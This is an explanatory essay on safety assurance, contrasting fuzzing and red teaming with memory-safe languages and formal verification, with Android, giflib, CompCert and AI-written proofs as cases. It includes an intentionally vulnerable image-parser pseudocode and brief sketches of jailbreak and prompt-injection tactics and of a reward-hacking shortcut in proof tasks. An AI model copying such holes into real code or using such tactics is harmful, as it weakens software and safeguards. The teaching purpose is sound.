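# Adversarial Failure Search and Correctness by Construction in AI Safety Assurance

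## What are the two strategies, and what does each claim?

Safety assurance is the work of showing that a system is safe enough for a particular use. It consists of evidence, such as test results, proofs and operating records, and an argument for why that evidence shows the system is safe enough. Aircraft and railway regulators have demanded it for decades, and AI developers now face much the same demand.

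Engineers have two broad ways to earn that confidence. In failure search, they attack the system, look for inputs or situations in which it misbehaves, and repair what they find. This includes ordinary testing, bug bounties (payments to outsiders who report flaws) and red teaming, in which people deliberately try to make a system fail. In correctness by construction, they build the system so that a stated class of failure cannot occur while stated assumptions hold. Most serious projects do some of each, but the two strategies support different claims, as a very small program can illustrate.

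### A buffer overflow in an image parser

A parser is a program that reads a file and works out its contents. Take one for an invented greyscale image format. Every file opens with two fixed marker bytes, then gives the width in one byte and the height in another, then one byte for each pixel. The programmer expects small pictures and sets aside 1,024 bytes of memory, a buffer, to hold the pixels:

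```
if the first two bytes are not the marker: stop
n = width * height
i = 0
while i < n:
    buffer[i] = next byte of the file
    i = i + 1
```

A 30-by-30 picture needs 900 bytes and fits in the buffer. A 40-by-40 picture needs 1,600, so the last 576 are written to the memory beyond the buffer, which is called a buffer overflow. C does not prevent this, and if the neighbouring memory determines what the program does next, whoever made the picture may be able to take control of the program. Real image libraries have had this flaw. Isosceles' *The WebP 0day* describes how Google patched a buffer overflow in 2023 in the library that its Chrome browser used for WebP images, when attackers already had a working exploit.

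Fuzzing, the usual way to search for such a bug, runs the program on many generated inputs and records which ones crash it. Random guessing does badly even on this toy example, since only one random file in 65,536 starts with the right two marker bytes. Better fuzzers track which parts of the code each input reaches. Zalewski (2014), in *Pulling JPEGs out of thin air*, gave his fuzzer, afl, a text file containing only the word "hello" and pointed it at a program that expects JPEG images. One change to the first byte had no visible effect but sent execution down a slightly different path, so afl kept the altered file and mutated it further. A change to the second byte then completed a valid header. After about six hours on an eight-core machine, afl had produced a real, blank image 3 pixels wide and 784 tall. AFL++, a successor to afl, follows the same rule, according to its documentation.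 It adds files that reach new program states to a queue of starting points without automatically replacing the older ones.

A fuzzer of this kind could find the toy parser's marker one byte at a time, in hundreds of tries. Once it has the marker, about 92 percent of the possible width and height pairs will cause an overflow, because they multiply to more than 1,024. An overflow does not always cause a crash, so testers usually add a sanitizer, extra code that halts the program at its first bad memory access. They then have a specific file that breaks the parser.

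The programmer then adds a line that rejects any picture of more than 1,024 pixels, and that file no longer does harm. Suppose the format also has a colour mode, with three bytes per pixel. A 30-by-30 colour picture passes the new check and still writes 2,700 bytes. The fuzzer may well find this too, but probably not if the colour code runs only after an all-or-nothing comparison, such as the fourteen-character password check that Zalewski gives as an example of what defeats afl. A nearly right password takes the program no further than a completely wrong one, so the fuzzer has no partial success to build on, and a blind guess succeeds about once in 5 × 10³³ tries.

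A bounds-checked language guards against the same bug even if nobody has found it. Before every write, the program compares the index with the size of the buffer and stops with an error if the index is out of range. The 40-by-40 picture fills all 1,024 places, and the next write halts the parser. The colour picture also halts it, even though nobody anticipated colour. An attacker can still make the parser stop, which is a nuisance and in some settings a danger, but cannot write into the neighbouring memory. This protection is called memory safety, which means that the program never reads or writes memory it should not.

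According to the documentation of Wuffs, a small programming language for handling untrusted files, each check takes nanoseconds, which can add up to milliseconds on a megapixel image. Wuffs avoids this delay by having the compiler do the checking before the program runs. Wuffs' *Wrangling Untrusted File Formats Safely* says "If it compiles, it is safe", and in the same passage limits that promise to buffer overflows, arithmetic overflows and one kind of pointer error.

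Formal verification goes further and proves, with a proof that a machine checks, that a program meets a specification. The standard notation is the Hoare triple {P} S {Q}, which Runge, Bordis and colleagues (2022), in *Flexible Correct-by-Construction Programming*, explain as follows: if condition P holds and statement S runs, then S terminates and condition Q holds. For a loop, the prover needs an invariant, a condition that is true before the loop and stays true after every pass. Here a suitable one is

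0 ≤ i ≤ n ≤ 1024.

With the programmer's size check in place and only greyscale pictures allowed, the invariant holds at the start, when i = 0. Inside the loop, i < n ≤ 1024, so the write stays within the buffer. Adding one to i leaves i ≤ n, so the invariant still holds after each pass. The quantity n − i shrinks by one each time and never goes below zero, so the loop ends. This short proof covers every possible greyscale file. Without the size check, the proof fails at its first step, because n can be as large as 65,025. With the check in place but colour mode added, it fails at the same step, because n is now three times the number of pixels and can reach 3,072. The failed proof shows the engineer the mistake before any bad file exists.

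### A failure found and a guarantee given

Write X for the set of all inputs and Safe(x) for "the program behaves acceptably on input x". A successful search establishes

∃x ∈ X: ¬Safe(x),

that is, at least one bad input exists. A guarantee has the form

A ⇒ ∀x ∈ X: Safe(x),

so that if the assumptions A hold, every input is safe. One bad input refutes the claim that all inputs are safe. A million good ones do not establish it, unless a million is all there are.

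The computer scientist Edsger Dijkstra gave the classic statement of this in *Notes on Structured Programming* (1970). He considered a circuit in his university's computer that multiplied two 27-bit numbers. There were 2⁵⁴ possible multiplications, and at some tens of microseconds each, testing them all would take more than 10,000 years. The circuit would perform almost none of them in its lifetime, but its users needed every one to be right because nobody knew in advance which ones would come up. Dijkstra concluded that testing can be used "to show the presence of bugs, but never to show ...".

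Dijkstra's remark is too strong if taken literally. The newsletter essay *Testing can show the presence of bugs but not the absence* points out that a function with finitely many inputs can be tested on all of them. This is now nearly practical for Dijkstra's own example, a multiplier, and would take about seven months at a billion multiplications a second. For 64-bit numbers, though, it would take some 10²² years, and the number of possible thousand-byte image files has over 2,400 digits. Dijkstra's argument was also about mechanisms treated as black boxes. He wrote that the way out was to take the mechanism's structure into account, as the loop invariant does. A coverage-guided fuzzer also uses information about the program's structure, but only to choose its next input, so its results still apply only to the inputs it ran.

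He had a second reason for wanting more than samples. If a program has N components and each is correct with probability p, the whole program is correct with probability roughly pᴺ. For a thousand components at 99 percent each, the chance that the whole program is correct is about one in 23,000.

A file that crashes the parser is evidence about the real program on a real machine, including the compiler and memory chips used. Anyone can run the program on that file again. A guarantee covers every input but depends on A. If some part of A is false, the guarantee may provide no assurance, possibly without anyone noticing.

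### Where "correctness by construction" comes from

The wish to reason about programs as well as run them is about as old as programming. Thomas (2017), in *Making Software 'Correct by Construction'*, traces it to a 1949 paper in which Alan Turing proposed annotating a program's flow chart with claims that should hold at each point. While other researchers tried to prove finished programs correct, Dijkstra (1968), in *A Constructive Approach to the Problem of Program Correctness*, derived a program step by step from its specification, using two processes that share a buffer as his example. In another note of the period, *A preliminary investigation into Computer Assisted Programming*, he called debugging a dead alley and wanted to "prevent bugs from entering the construction". In his Turing Award lecture, *The Humble Programmer* (1972), he advised developing the proof and the program together.

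He also predicted in that lecture that before the decade ended, programmers would build systems "virtually free of bugs" at a few percent of the then-current cost, but this did not happen. His own notes show part of the difficulty. In them he proves a two-line search loop correct, and the proof is so long that he admits it infuriates him.

Dijkstra's line of work continues as a formal method. The developer starts with a Hoare triple that has a hole in place of the program, then fills the hole using a fixed set of refinement rules, each of which preserves correctness. When no holes remain, the program meets its specification. Runge and colleagues list eight such rules and acknowledge that the method feels rigid and needs special tools.

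The phrase also has a more industrial history at Praxis, a British software company. Martin Croxford of Praxis and James Sutton of Lockheed used it in *Breaking through the V and V bottleneck* (1995), about avionics software for the C-130J transport aircraft. Later writers usually cite Anthony Hall and Roderick Chapman's 2002 account of the Praxis process. Hall's *Correctness by Construction* describes the process as combining careful requirements work, formal methods and system architecture with automated analysis in SPARK, a restricted version of the Ada language. One of its key principles, according to Chapman's *Recent results with Correctness by Construction and SPARK* (2005), was to make errors hard to introduce. The process still included testing, but Hall (2019) says this was to confirm that the software works, whereas conventional projects use testing for debugging.

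Runge and colleagues warn readers not to confuse the two traditions, which support different kinds of claims. Hall reports fewer than 0.1 defects per thousand lines of code, an excellent rate that still allows almost a hundred defects in a million lines. A refinement proof or a bounds check supports the stronger claim that a named failure cannot happen. That claim matters more for safety assurance, whether it comes from a proof, a programming language or the design of the system.

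### What a guarantee depends on

Every such claim needs a specification, a precise statement of what the system must or must not do. "Never write outside the buffer" is a good one because a machine can check it, but it is narrow, since a parser that turns every picture black would satisfy it. Thomas requires much more of correct software. It must perform all the required functions and nothing else, do so on every possible input, and come with strong evidence that outsiders can verify. He adds that requirements in plain English are almost always incomplete and contradictory, so somebody has to translate them into mathematics and can make mistakes in doing so.

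The specification is therefore part of the trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for the guarantee to hold. The loop proof covers the parser's source code. It applies to the running program only if the compiler translates that code faithfully, the processor behaves as documented, and the software that checked the proof is sound.

A threat model specifies which attackers, inputs and conditions the claim covers. The parser's threat model would include a stranger who sends a malicious picture, but not a burglar who replaces the program on the disk. Security engineers group flaws with a common cause into vulnerability classes, such as buffer overflows, and guarantees generally remove one class at a time. The residual risk consists of the failures that no guarantee covers and no search has found, and nobody can measure it directly.

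### Language models

A language model, the kind of system behind ChatGPT or Claude, is hard to fit into this scheme. Its behaviour comes from billions of numbers called weights, which start at random values. During training, an algorithm goes through enormous amounts of text and repeatedly adjusts the weights to make the word fragment that came next in the text slightly more probable. Further training rewards answers that people or automated graders prefer, and solutions that pass a check. Engineers write the arithmetic and the training procedure, but they don't write the resulting behaviour themselves. A dangerous answer therefore can't be traced to a missing line of code, as the parser's fault could, and correcting it changes many weights at once, which affects other answers in ways that are hard to predict.

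Developers therefore rely heavily on search. *Red Teaming AI Red Teaming* (Majumdar, Pendleton and Gupta, 2025) traces red teaming from Prussian war games of the early nineteenth century, in which red pieces stood for the enemy, through Cold War simulations to computer security. Red teamers interact with a language model to uncover wrong or harmful behaviour. They might rephrase a forbidden request as fiction, spread it over many messages, or hide instructions in a document that the model will read. Increasingly, other models generate the attacks. The developer then retrains the model or adds a filter, and the testers try again. Majumdar and colleagues think the practice has become too narrow because most current work tests finished models. They want red teams to question a project from its inception, including whether it needs AI at all.

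Even the narrow version is harder than fuzzing. A sanitizer detects invalid memory accesses automatically, but a person or another model has to judge whether an answer is harmful, and judges disagree. The same prompt can also produce a harmless answer ninety-nine times and a harmful one on the hundredth.

Some large software developers have decided in favor of correctness by construction. Google wrote in 2024 that even thorough fuzzing "does not provide high assurance", and reported that memory flaws had fallen from 76 to 24 percent of Android's vulnerabilities as new code moved to memory-safe languages. However, "do no harm" has no one-line specification of the kind that exists for memory flaws. Developers can begin searching for failures with less agreement about what safety means, and AI systems can now do some of the searching. With limited people and time before a release, an AI developer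 has to decide how much of each to devote to attacking the model and how much to building something, inside the model or around it, that rules out a class of failure.

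## How far have memory-safe languages reduced vulnerabilities?

The best-documented large case is Android, Google's phone operating system. Memory flaws continued to fall as a share of its vulnerabilities, from 24 percent in 2024 to less than 20 percent in 2025. Google already used the memory-safe languages Java and Kotlin for much of the system, and it introduced Rust for the low-level parts that it would otherwise have written in C or C++.

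### How Rust excludes memory errors

Java and Kotlin programs rely on a garbage collector, a background process that frees a piece of memory only once nothing refers to it. Garbage collection slows programs and gives programmers less control over memory, which is why operating-system programmers long stayed with C and C++. Rust's compiler works out when most memory can be safely freed before the program runs.

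Every value in a Rust program has exactly one owner, and the program frees the value's memory when the owner goes out of use. Other code can borrow the value through a reference, under rules that the compiler enforces. No reference may outlive the value it points to. At any moment a value may have many read-only references or a single reference that can change it, but not both. Take this fragment:

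```
let mut row = vec![10, 20, 30];
let first = &row[0];
row.push(40);
println!("{}", first);
```

The fragment makes a list, borrows the first element, appends a number and prints the borrowed element. If the list has no spare room, appending moves it to a larger piece of memory and frees the old one. Printing `first` would then read freed memory, an error called a use-after-free. The equivalent C++ compiles and often seems to work, but the Rust compiler rejects the fragment because the third line changes the list while `first` still borrows it. The same rule excludes data races, where two threads use the same memory at once and at least one writes to it.

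Buffer overflows need a different remedy because the compiler often cannot determine an index in advance. Rust therefore checks the index against the buffer's length at run time, which would have stopped the toy image parser at its 1,025th pixel.

Some necessary operations, such as controlling hardware or calling a C library, fall outside these rules. A programmer puts them in a block marked `unsafe`, which permits a few extra operations and leaves most of the checks on. Good practice is to wrap the block in a function that other code cannot misuse, so that reviewers have little code to examine. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that about 4 percent of Android's Rust code is in such blocks. The trusted base includes these blocks, Rust's standard library and the compiler. *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* (Bae, 2026) reports memory flaws in the library, and *Claude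 Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) describes one in the compiler.

The approach can also be used in existing languages. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets a script into a web page that someone else opens, typically because the site inserted untrusted text into the page as if it were code. A safe interface prevents this by accepting only text of a special type, which can be created only in ways that neutralise any script it contains. A programmer who forgets this step gets an error message instead of creating a vulnerability. Google credits this approach, which it calls Safe Coding, with "remarkable success" in eliminating cross-site scripting, and presents the move to Rust as an extension of it.

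### Android's record from 2019 to 2025

Google's *Memory Safe Languages in Android 13* (2022) counts the critical and high-severity flaws in Android's security bulletins, including those outsiders reported for a reward and those Google's staff found. Memory flaws fell from 223 in 2019 to 85 in 2022, and LWN's *Memory Safe Languages in Android 13 (Google security blog)* gives their share in 2022 as 35 percent. Google had counted 27 by September 2024 and extrapolated to 36 for the full year. The last column below is calculated from the counts and shares, assuming both cover the same flaws.

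| Year | Memory-safety flaws | Share of all flaws | Other flaws (implied) |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2019 | 223 | 76% | about 70 |
| 2022 | 85 | 35% | about 158 |
| 2024 | 36 (extrapolated) | 24% | about 114 |
| 2025 | – | under 20% | – |

Part of the fall in memory flaws' share came from a rise in other kinds of flaw. Had the other flaws stayed at 70, the memory share in 2024 would have been 34 percent, not 24. The counts are therefore better evidence than the percentages, and they dropped by 84 percent while the amount of code grew. The number of memory flaws rose slightly in 2023, when Google received unusually many reports of all kinds, but their share kept falling. Google adds that memory flaws tend to be more severe and easier to reach remotely than other flaws, so risk probably fell by more than the total number of flaws did.

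It is harder to say whether Rust, Java and Kotlin caused the decline. In 2022, Google pointed out that the share of memory flaws closely tracked the languages used for new code, but warned that correlation is not necessarily causation. Android 13, released that year, was the first version in which most new code was memory-safe. But Google was also making its C and C++ safer. *Practical Security in Production* (Dionne, Shavrick and Varlamov, 2025) describes how Google rolled out a hardened version of the C++ standard library across the company. Such measures reduce risk even where no Rust is used. Google mentions its work on memory-unsafe code as a possible reason why Android's flaws fell faster than its model predicted.

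The counts also depend on what Google classifies as a vulnerability. In *justafewbugs*, Li-Yates (2026), an independent researcher, describes filing 95 reports with Google's reward programme for Android and Google devices and later comparing the closed ones with the shipped software. In eight cases, Google had closed the report as a duplicate or as no vulnerability, yet the code now had a fix at the place the report named. Li-Yates received $250 in total and has a grievance. If the account is right, the published totals are too low, but that would produce a false downward trend only if Google had become stricter over the years about accepting reports, or about accepting reports of memory flaws in particular.

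### Why Google could leave most old code alone

Android's engineers rewrote little existing code, and in 2024 most of the system's code was still in memory-unsafe languages. Google focused on new code and on making Rust work smoothly with C++ and Kotlin, and it gave the Rust Foundation $1 million for interoperability work.

This worked because flaws are concentrated in recent code. Google had noticed the pattern in Android by 2021. A year later, in *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?*, Alexopoulos and colleagues measured vulnerability lifetimes across open-source projects and found, in Google's summary, that the vast majority of vulnerabilities sit in new or recently modified code. Google models the lifetimes with an exponential distribution. If L is the mean lifetime of a flaw, the density of flaws in code of age t is

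density(t) = density(0) × exp(−t/L).

With a mean flaw lifetime (L) of 2.5 years, the value Google used in its simulation, five-year-old code has exp(−2), or about 14 percent, of the flaws it had when new, which is a 7.4-fold reduction. The lifetimes Alexopoulos and colleagues measured give a 3.4-fold reduction, which corresponds to a mean lifetime of about 4.1 years.

Google then simulated a codebase that doubles in size every six years, with a mean flaw lifetime of 2.5 years and a ten-year transition to safe languages for new code. In the final year memory flaws drop sharply, although the program contains more unsafe code than ever. The result looks paradoxical until one writes down what happens to V, the number of flaws present:

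dV/dt = d × u(t) − V/L,

where u(t) is the amount of unsafe code that programmers add per year and d is the number of flaws per line in it. The total amount of unsafe code does not appear in the equation. Suppose, with invented figures, that a team introduces 100 memory flaws a year. With L = 2.5 the number present settles at 250. The team then moves nine tenths of its new work to a safe language, and introduces ten a year. After five years about 55 flaws remain, a drop of 78 percent, even though the team has deleted nothing and has kept adding some unsafe code. With a mean lifetime of 4.1 years the drop would be 64 percent.

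Code does not become safer just by getting older, though. The term V/L represents people finding and fixing flaws, so Google's decline in vulnerabilities owes a good deal to failure search, which kept removing flaws from old code while safe languages reduced the supply of new ones. If the searching stopped, L would become infinite and the old flaws would remain. The average lifetime also leaves out flaws that nobody has found, because a flaw's lifetime can be measured only after it is found. The model assumes that these flaws follow the same pattern as the known ones. That assumption looks less secure now that, as Groß (2026) notes in *Fuzzers vs. AI*, hundreds and sometimes thousands of new bugs have turned up in heavily fuzzed code.

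### One near-miss in five million lines

Comparing Rust code with C and C++ code is the more direct test. By late 2025, Android contained roughly five million lines of Rust, in which Google had found one potential memory-safety vulnerability. Vander Stoep calculates this as 0.2 per million lines, compared with a historical rate of close to 1,000 per million for Android's C and C++ code.

The single case, CVE-2025-48530, was a buffer overflow caused by unsafe code in CrabbyAVIF, a Rust library for AVIF images. Google fixed it before any public release. Even if it had shipped, Android's default memory allocator, Scudo, would have stopped attackers from exploiting it. Scudo surrounds large blocks of memory with inaccessible guard pages, so an overflow that reaches one causes a crash instead of silent corruption. The crash helped Google notice the flaw, but the crash reports did not make clear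 that an overflow had caused it, which slowed the response. Not every Android device uses Scudo, and Google is still trying to make it compulsory for manufacturers.

One event is thin evidence for a rate. If flaws turn up independently, their number follows a Poisson distribution, and the one-sided 95 percent upper limit is the mean m at which one event or fewer would occur only 5 percent of the time:

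exp(−m) × (1 + m) = 0.05, so m ≈ 4.74.

Divided by five million lines, that is 0.95 per million. The gap to C and C++ is still about a thousandfold.

The gap could be an artefact of age, because much of the Rust is young and people have had less time to find its flaws. The decay model gives a rough correction. If the average line is a year old and L is 2.5 years, people have found about a third of the flaws so far, so the upper limit rises to about 2.9 per million and the gap shrinks to about 350-fold. The average line of Rust would have to be about a day old for age to explain a thousandfold gap by itself.

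Differences in what the programs do could also skew the comparison, because Vander Stoep does not match Rust components with C++ components that do the same job. If Google had used Rust mainly for code that handles no hostile input, Rust would look safer than it is. But even if we arbitrarily assume that this exaggerates Rust's advantage tenfold, and also correct for age, Rust's vulnerability rate is still about 35 times lower. At least some of the Rust code can receive hostile input, since the near-miss was in an image library. Google has also replaced the parsers for PNG images, JSON data and web fonts with Rust versions in Chromium, Chrome's open-source base.

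People may look less for memory errors in Rust because they expect to find none. This would surely lower the rate of discovery, but it would have to do so several hundredfold to explain the whole difference from C and C++. Unsafe blocks are a useful check because they are the obvious place to look. They make up 4% of the five million lines of Rust, or 200,000 lines, which would contain about 200 vulnerabilities at the C and C++ rate. Google has found one. Vander Stoep says Google does not know for certain why unsafe Rust does so well, but suggests that the remaining compiler checks, the habit of wrapping unsafe code in safe functions and the extra attention from reviewers all contribute.

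All these figures come from Google, which has invested heavily in Rust and wants others to adopt it. The exact multiple is unreliable, but the reduction in this one class of flaw in new code is still well over tenfold after every correction above.

### What switching costs, and what a rewrite involves

Vander Stoep reports that safer code was also faster to develop at Android. Compared with C++ changes of similar size, Rust changes needed about 20 percent fewer revisions and spent about 25 percent less time in review. Among medium and large changes, engineers withdrew Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ ones. Many of the same developers work in both languages, which removes one source of bias, but the work was not randomly assigned, and newer projects may be easier to change.

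Rust was harder to introduce in firmware. Google's *Bringing Rust to Pixel Baseband* (2026) describes adding a Rust parser for internet address lookups to the modem software in Pixel phones. The modem became slower and used more power because the build process had accidentally replaced its optimized routines for copying and filling memory with Rust's generic ones.

Rewriting old code used to be too expensive to do on a large scale, though people did it for particularly exposed components. Crane (2024), in *Porting C to Rust for a Fast and Safe AV1 Media Decoder*, describes one such port, of the video decoder dav1d. AI has made translation far cheaper. Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* presents an AI-assisted rewrite of giflib, a widely used C library for GIF images, and 何 (2026), in *谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞*, sets out the steps. Two engineers, Bastian Kersting and Max Hils, gave about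 3,000 lines of C to Google's Gemini model and asked for equivalent Rust. They kept the original function names so existing C programs could still call the library. Gemini's first version had mistakes in which code owned which memory and for how long, especially at the boundary with C, and people had to correct them.

Rust's rules do not guarantee that a new library will produce the same images as the old one, so the engineers tested for this. They decoded more than 30 million real GIF files with both versions and required bit-identical output. They also ran a fuzzer for six days and 200 million iterations, which exposed two faults in the original C code, an edge case in decompression and a buffer overflow introduced by an earlier patch. An outside researcher later reported the overflow, which a remote attacker could use for denial of service, according to *CVE-2026-26740* in the US government's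 National Vulnerability Database (NVD). By then Google's servers were running the Rust version, so the flaw did not affect them.

The GIF port covers only one library, but it avoids the main weakness of the Android comparison because the two languages do exactly the same job. The port was about as fast as the original. Google also removed the sandbox in which it had confined GIF decoding, which cut the longest delays but left the decoder with one less layer of defence. That loss could matter, because a second layer of defence made a mistake in CrabbyAVIF's unsafe Rust harmless.

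giflib was also an easy target, small and with a working original to compare against. Other AI-assisted ports have had similar help. The Ladybird browser project moved parts of its JavaScript engine from C++ to Rust, and its founder, Andreas Kling, chose those parts partly because the standard JavaScript test suite covers them thoroughly, as Willison (2026) reports. Bun (2026), which makes software for running JavaScript, rewrote its product from Zig, a language with manual memory management, using a pre-release Claude model from Anthropic, its owner. Willison (2026) quotes Bun's founder, Jarred Sumner, on the motive: he was tired of going to sleep worrying about crashes.

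Daniel Stenberg, who leads the data-transfer tool curl, doubts that cheap translation solves much. *Actual curl rewrites in rust* (Stenberg, 2026) discusses two AI rewrites of curl, one with a claimed cost of $8,600. He attributes their success to curl's thorough documentation, its thousands of test cases and the years of curl code in the models' training data. In his view, writing the code once was never the hard part. Willison (2026) quotes him as saying that the curl project made about 200 bug fixes in a little over three weeks that neither rewrite has. Somebody has to keep a rewrite up to date for as long as people use it. Google avoided that problem with giflib by adopting the Rust version itself, but a port that the original maintainers reject becomes a separate program that may fall behind the original.

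### The 2026 bulletins

Google fixed 326 Android vulnerabilities in its October to December 2026 security updates, more than twice the roughly 150 that its figures imply for all of 2024. At first, this looks like a reversal. Google fixed 25 vulnerabilities in October (Arghire, *Android's October 2026 Updates Patch 25 Vulnerabilities*, 2026), 216 in November (窓の杜, *2026年11月のAndroidセキュリティ情報、216件の脆弱性*, 2026), and 85 in December. It rated 23 of the November vulnerabilities critical and 193 high.

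However, the totals may not cover the same things. Jornal 24 Horas' *Google corrige 216 falhas de segurança no Android em atualização* (2026) lists 65 flaws for November in the Framework (the layer that apps call), 53 in the System component, one in the Android Runtime, and 97 in the kernel and in parts from chip companies such as Qualcomm and MediaTek. Google's share of under 20 percent for 2025 covers its own and open-source code in the Android platform. It would exclude chip makers' proprietary drivers, and Google does not choose the language those are written in.

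These totals also don't show how many of the flaws involve memory. Android's bulletins classify flaws by component, severity and effect, and an effect such as "elevation of privilege" can come from a memory error or a missing permission check. The Framework is mostly Java and Kotlin, so its flaws are probably logic errors. If every flaw outside the Framework and the Runtime involved memory, the share for November would be 69 percent. That is an upper limit, and the true share could be far lower. The month's most severe flaw, which let an attacker run code remotely without any action by the user, was in the Framework.

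December's list has the same limitation. CyberSec24's *Android December Update Fixes 85 Security Flaws* (2026) reports that 50 of the 85 flaws could give an attacker or a malicious app extra privileges, but this doesn't identify their causes. The Hacker News' *Google Fixes Android Video Decoder and IMS Flaws That Could Allow RCE* (2026) singles out two especially dangerous flaws that could let an attacker run code without any action by the user. RodHat's *Android 17 QPR2* (2026) reports that one is a write outside a buffer in the MPEG-2 video decoder and the other is a race condition that corrupts memory in the software for carrier voice services. RodHat also lists an integer overflow that an attacker can exploit from nearby.

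Safe Rust would have blocked the MPEG-2 write with a bounds check, and its borrowing rules prevent the usual kind of race that corrupts memory. Integer overflows are mostly dangerous when a program uses the wrong number as a size or an index, and the bounds check applies there too. MPEG-2 dates from the 1990s, so its decoder is probably old C or C++, the kind of code Google decided to leave in place. People have had decades to find flaws in such code, and according to the decay model it should have almost none left.

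## What does formal verification remove, and what does it cost?

Formal verification can guarantee properties of old C code, such as Android's MPEG-2 decoder, without a rewrite in Rust. It proves a theorem about the existing code, and the theorem can cover far more than the absence of memory errors. For decades this was so expensive that hardly anyone outside research attempted it. In 2026 AI agents began to write most of the proofs in several large projects, which lowered the cost and made it more important to check exactly what they had proved.

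### A proof about a short function

CPython, the program that runs nearly all Python code, has to work out how many numbers a range contains. Andrews and Zhang (2026), in *Formalizing CPython*, reproduce the C function that does this. In simplified notation, where `/` divides and rounds down, its logic is:

```
if step is positive and lo < hi:
    result = 1 + (hi - lo - 1) / step
if step is negative and hi < lo:
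    result = 1 + (lo - hi - 1) / (-step)
in all other cases:
    result = 0
```

In Python, `range(0, 10, 3)` means the numbers 0, 3, 6 and 9. The function correctly calculates their count as 1 + 9/3 = 4. To prove that it is correct for every range, an engineer needs a specification, a model of the machine, a proof and a checker.

The specification has to define "right" without repeating the code. For a positive step, a suitable one is

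result = the number of whole numbers k ≥ 0 for which lo + k × step < hi.

The model describes mathematically what each operation does. On a typical 64-bit Linux machine, the inputs are signed integers from −2⁶³ to 2⁶³ − 1. The C code does its arithmetic with unsigned integers, which run from 0 to 2⁶⁴ − 1 and then wrap round to 0.

To prove this, suppose step > 0 and lo < hi. Since all the numbers are whole, lo + k × step < hi holds exactly when k × step ≤ hi − lo − 1. So k can be any whole number from 0 up to (hi − lo − 1)/step, rounded down, and the number of such values is one more than that rounded quotient, as in the code. The engineer must also show that the machine computes this formula correctly. The value of hi − lo − 1 is at least 0 and at most 2⁶⁴ − 2, so it fits in an unsigned number, and adding 1 to the quotient cannot wrap around. The proof for a negative step is symmetric, and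 in all remaining cases the range is empty.

If the programmer had used signed arithmetic, the proof would have failed at the step showing that the difference fits in a signed 64-bit number. For a range from −6 × 10¹⁸ to 6 × 10¹⁸, the difference is 12 × 10¹⁸, which is larger than the largest such number. Somebody who tested only a few hundred everyday ranges would never notice this error.

Engineers write formal proofs in a language like Lean, Isabelle or Rocq (formerly Coq), and a small program called the kernel checks every inference. This makes proof writing a good task for AI. Kleppmann (2025) points out in *Prediction* that it doesn't matter if a language model hallucinates, because the kernel rejects any invalid proof and the model has to try again.

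Andrews and Zhang had Anthropic's Claude Opus 5.5 copy CPython's functions into Lean line by line and prove theorems about the copies. Such a theorem is of little use if the copy is wrong, so the agents first compared each copy with real Python on tens of thousands of inputs. The link between the theorem and the C code therefore rests on testing. By November 2026, 4,071 functions had also passed a review by a second agent, and the project had covered 16 percent of CPython and produced 418 bug reports. About 55 of those reports were for bugs that let ordinary Python code crash Python or corrupt memory.

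### seL4 and CompCert

The best-known handwritten proof is of seL4, a microkernel, which is the small core of an operating system that controls access to memory and the processor. According to Kleppmann, as of 2009 seL4 had 8,700 lines of C, and its proof had taken 20 person-years and 200,000 lines of Isabelle. That is 23 lines of proof and half a working day of proof work for every line of C. Building the kernel took only about two person-years, according to Lim, Tu and colleagues (2026) in *Pre-QED*.

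With that effort, the engineers proved functional correctness, which means that the C code does only what an abstract specification of the kernel allows. The proof rules out memory errors and mistakes that no compiler would detect, such as granting a program an access right that the specification does not allow. The 2009 proof covered the C source and assumed that the compiler was correct.

Compilers sometimes produce incorrect code. Xavier Leroy and colleagues used Rocq to develop CompCert, a C compiler, and to prove that its compiled programs behave only in ways their source programs allow. CompCert gave researchers a rare chance to run the same failure search on verified and unverified software. *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (Yang, Chen and colleagues, 2011) introduced Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs, each with a single correct output. Csmith compiles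 each program with several compilers and compares the results. If they differ, at least one compiler is wrong.

Over three years, Yang and colleagues reported more than 325 previously unknown compiler bugs. Except for CompCert, every compiler they tested silently produced wrong code because of bugs in its middle part, where most optimisation happens. They found no wrong-code bugs in CompCert's verified passes after about six years of processor time. The wrong-code bugs they found in CompCert were in parts without a proof. CompCert is much smaller than a compiler like GCC and attempts fewer optimisations, so one would expect it to have fewer bugs anyway. But size alone would not explain why the wrong-code bugs they found were all outside the verified passes.

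*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (jmason.ie, 2026) quotes a similar result from a 2026 test that fuzzed a Lean-verified version of the compression library zlib. In 105 million runs, the verified code had no memory errors, and the two bugs found were outside what the proofs covered.

### 239 fuzz tests turned into theorems

Few open-source libraries have a formal specification, and writing one by hand for each would be slow. Anthropic and Theorem, a verification startup, used the libraries' existing tests. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 libraries.

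All 123 libraries take part in OSS-Fuzz, Google's fuzzing service for open-source software. Each has at least one harness, a short program that accepts any string of bytes and passes it to the library. Lim and colleagues describe what Anthropic and Theorem did with the harnesses. Their pipeline compiles a harness and its library into one program for RISC-V, a processor design with a fairly simple instruction set. It compiles C and C++ code with sanitizers, so a proof that the program never crashes also covers memory errors. It then combines the machine code with Theorem's mathematical models of RISC-V and Linux, and generates a theorem without anyone writing a specification by hand:

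for every input x smaller than 64 MB and every environment e in the model, the program exits normally.

An environment is one combination of memory layout and responses from the operating system. The number of possible inputs has more than 150 million digits. The theorem is stronger than a bounds check because it also rules out programs that halt with an error at a bad write or loop forever on some input. Some harnesses compress data, decompress it and compare the result with the original, and the theorem also covers that round trip.

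Claude then tries to prove the theorem in Rocq. If it finds a real bug, it patches the library, the pipeline generates a new theorem for the patched program, and Claude tries to prove that one instead. Claude could cheat by patching the program to do nothing, since such a program never crashes. Anthropic and Theorem therefore penalised patches, gave extra credit for proving which inputs a patch affects, and logged and audited all patches.

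Claude completed the proof for 239 harnesses. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) gives the total length as about 180 million lines, with about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 instructions. *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) puts the total at a billion. At 600,000 lines each, 239 proofs would come to about 143 million lines, so OpenNET's figure looks more plausible for the finished proofs. Instead of reading the proofs, which the Rocq kernel has checked, people need to examine the trusted base: the harnesses and theorems, the models of RISC-V and Linux, and Rocq itself along with the computer it runs on.

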